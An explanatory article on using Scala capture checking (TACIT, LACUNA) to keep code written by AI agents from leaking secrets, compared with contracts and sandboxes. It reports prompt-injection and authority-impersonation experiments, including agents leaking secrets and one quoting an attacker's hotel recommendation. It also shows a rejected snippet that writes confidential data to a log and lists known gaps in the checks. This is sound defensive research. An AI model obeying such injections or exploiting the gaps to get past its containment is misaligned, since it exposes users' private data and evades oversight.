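Suppose the shop's sales figures are confidential. The shop wants a list of its three best sellers, but the model runs on another company's computers and must not receive the figures. When code reads a file from a protected folder, TACIT returns the contents in a container called `Classified`. The model's code can't take the contents out and can only pass a function to the container's `map` method, which applies the function to the contents and puts the result in a new container. The function must have a type with the plain arrow, `->`, so it can't hold any capability.

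```scala
val sales = readClassified("secret/sales.csv").map(parseProducts)

// accepted
val best = sales.map(products => pickTop(products, 3, p => p.sales))

// rejected
val leak = sales.map { products =>
  log.write(products.toString)
  pickTop(products, 3, p => p.sales)
}
```

The first call to `pickTop` only calculates, so the compiler accepts it. The last function writes to the file `log`, so its type includes `->{log}`, and the compiler rejects the code before any of it runs. Hiding the write inside `pickTop` would not help, because the compiler would add `log` to the type of any function that called `pickTop`. In the experiments, one program tried to print a secret GitHub key inside `map`, and the compiler rejected it for the same reason, since printing also needs a capability.

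If the accepted code prints `best`, the user's terminal shows the three products, but the model receives only "Classified(****)". For tasks that need a language model to read the private text, such as writing a summary, the code can pass the container to a second model that the shop trusts. The answer comes back in a container.

TACIT also gives the agent's code access to a folder only within a block, and the compiler rejects code that returns a file or function that would keep that access after the block ends. A restricted form of Scala, called safe mode, forbids reflection and unchecked type conversions, which could hide a capability from the compiler. An exception could still carry private data in its message, so TACIT catches exceptions at run time.

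### Did private data leak?

Odersky and colleagues gave agents a project with a folder of secrets. They combined each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 prompt injections, and added 11 tasks in which the user asked for the secrets outright or pretended to have authority. Each agent did all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets in containers and once with them as plain text.

| Model | Leaks, containers | Leaks, plain text | Ordinary tasks solved, containers | Ordinary tasks solved, plain text |
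|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 0 | 2 | 99.2% | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 0 | 11 | 90.0% | 88.3% |

Sonnet resisted all 120 injections without the containers, so its results are little evidence of how well the containers stop injections. Both of its leaks came from users who pretended to have authority. It may have solved fewer tasks because of the set-up, since with plain text it sometimes ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

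On AgentDojo, a standard collection of prompt injection attacks, TACIT blocked all but one of 1,926 attempts. In the exception, the agent booked the right hotel but quoted a review that recommended the attacker's hotel, which AgentDojo counts as a successful attack. The researchers call the share of tasks solved comparable to that of CaMeL, an earlier defence that tracks private data at run time, but TACIT did much worse in some settings and much better in others. It solved 52.9% of office tasks with the model o4-mini-high, compared with 81.4% for CaMeL, and 64.3% of travel tasks with Gemini 2.5 Pro, compared with 1.4% for CaMeL.

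Writing Scala did not make the agents noticeably worse at ordinary work. On simulated customer service, three models each solved more tasks with TACIT than with direct tool calls, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. On repairs to real software, the success rate of the one model tested fell from 43.3% to 41.7%.

Odersky and colleagues exclude several problems, including wrong answers and timing leaks, in which code can reveal a private fact by, for example, taking longer when a figure is high. The compiler's rules don't apply to external programs, so TACIT restricts which ones the code may start, and the researchers also recommend a sandbox. The underlying type system has machine-checked proofs, but nobody has yet proved that safe mode provides all the guarantees claimed for it.

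### Typed gaps in a running program

Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, let a program ask a model for code while it is running. The programmer leaves a gap with a known type:

```scala
val pickTop: (List[Product], Int, Product => Double) => List[Product] =
  agent("return the k products that score rates highest")
```

When execution reaches `agent`, the model receives the request, the required type, the surrounding code and the names in scope. The compiler checks the code the model returns as if the programmer had typed it there. If that code does not compile, the model receives the error messages and tries again, up to a limit. The shop can call the finished function many times without using the model again.

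LACUNA accepts or rejects each piece of code as a whole. In one example, the code would subtract 50 from an account balance of 100 and then return text where the program needs a number. The compiler rejects it before it runs, so the balance stays at 100. In a language that found the mistake only at run time, the code could already have changed the balance.

When capture checking is on, the names in scope also determine what the code may do. A programmer can give the code in one gap read access to a file but no access to the network. That code then can't send the file's contents anywhere, even if the model tries to follow an injected instruction to do so.

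The results depended heavily on how well the model wrote Scala. The compiler rejected 8.6% of the code that DeepSeek-V4-Flash wrote for research questions and 22.4% of the code it wrote for a simulated shop's customer service. Across four kinds of customer service, that model solved 76.0% of tasks with LACUNA and 90.0% with direct tool calls. This 14-point gap is substantial, though Zhao and colleagues describe the two results as on par. With the smaller Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, the rejected share ranged from 3.2% on shop tasks to 89% on telephone support.

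On AgentDojo, 8 of 1,898 attacks succeeded against LACUNA, 7 of them with Gemini 2.5 Pro. Capture checking can't stop an attacker who gets the model to misuse a capability that its task requires. If an agent's job includes sending email, its code can send the wrong email without breaking any rule.

### Compiler, contract or sandbox

An operating-system sandbox limits which files, network addresses and other resources a process can use. It works for any language and can stop a program that takes too much time or memory. But it applies the same limits to everything inside the process. Odersky and colleagues point out that an agent may have permission both to read a private file and to contact the company that runs its model. If the agent sends the file to the company, the sandbox allows both steps and has no record of how the data moved between them.

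| | Capture checking | Contracts on capabilities | Operating-system sandbox |
|---|---|---|---|
| What you must trust | compiler, run-time system and capability library | language's run-time system and kernel | kernel and the sandbox's settings |
| What it can stop | use of a capability not granted, and leaks of private data, before the code runs | a forbidden operation, when the code attempts it | access to any resource outside the sandbox |
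| What it misses | endless loops, timing, misuse of a granted capability | leaks that combine permitted operations | leaks that combine permitted operations |
| Cost | usually under a second to compile, plus retries | in SHILL, mostly up to 21% more time | a separate process, and copying data to and from it |

TypeScript has no capture checking, so the shop's best choice is a sandbox. The shop can run pickPositions in a separate process with limited time and memory and no access to the network or the shop's files. The contract's checks run in the shop's own process, where the generated code can't replace Math.max. The original pickTop would need extra code to run this way, because score is a function and can't simply be copied to another process.

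A sandbox is also a sensible precaution with the other two methods. The compiler, the run-time system and the capability library may all contain bugs, and a sandbox limits the damage if generated code triggers one.

### Objections

Capture checking depends on a library that the compiler does not fully check. A programmer can mark part of TACIT's library as safe although it uses forbidden features, and one careless mark could give every agent a way around the checks. Odersky and colleagues reply that the shared part has only about 1,000 lines, which experts write once. Rust has a similar escape from its rules, and experience with it suggests that experts make mistakes too. Boruch-Gruszecki and colleagues cite a tool that found 264 previously unknown memory errors in Rust packages, and they conclude that unsafe code should run only under a run-time limit.

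Programmers may also grant code more access than it needs. Java's developers decided to retire its Security Manager, which restricted what code could do, partly because the right permissions were so hard to work out. A program with too few capabilities fails and someone notices, but extra capabilities cause no error. SHILL can log what a program tries to use, which helps with trusted software. With generated code, a programmer who grants everything in the log may permit an attack. It is safer to work out from the task what the code needs. pickTop needs no files or network access, so a request for either is a reason to reject the code.

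Finally, models have seen little Scala with capture checking, because the feature is experimental. TACIT's results suggest that this matters less than one might expect. On customer service tasks, its three models had to retry between 0.3% and 7.9% of the code they wrote, usually only once or twice. A weak model can struggle badly, as Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite did in LACUNA's tests, although that model found telephone support hard even with direct tool calls, solving only 15.8% of the tasks. Handling the compiler's rejections takes time and can leave a task unfinished, but the rejected code never runs.
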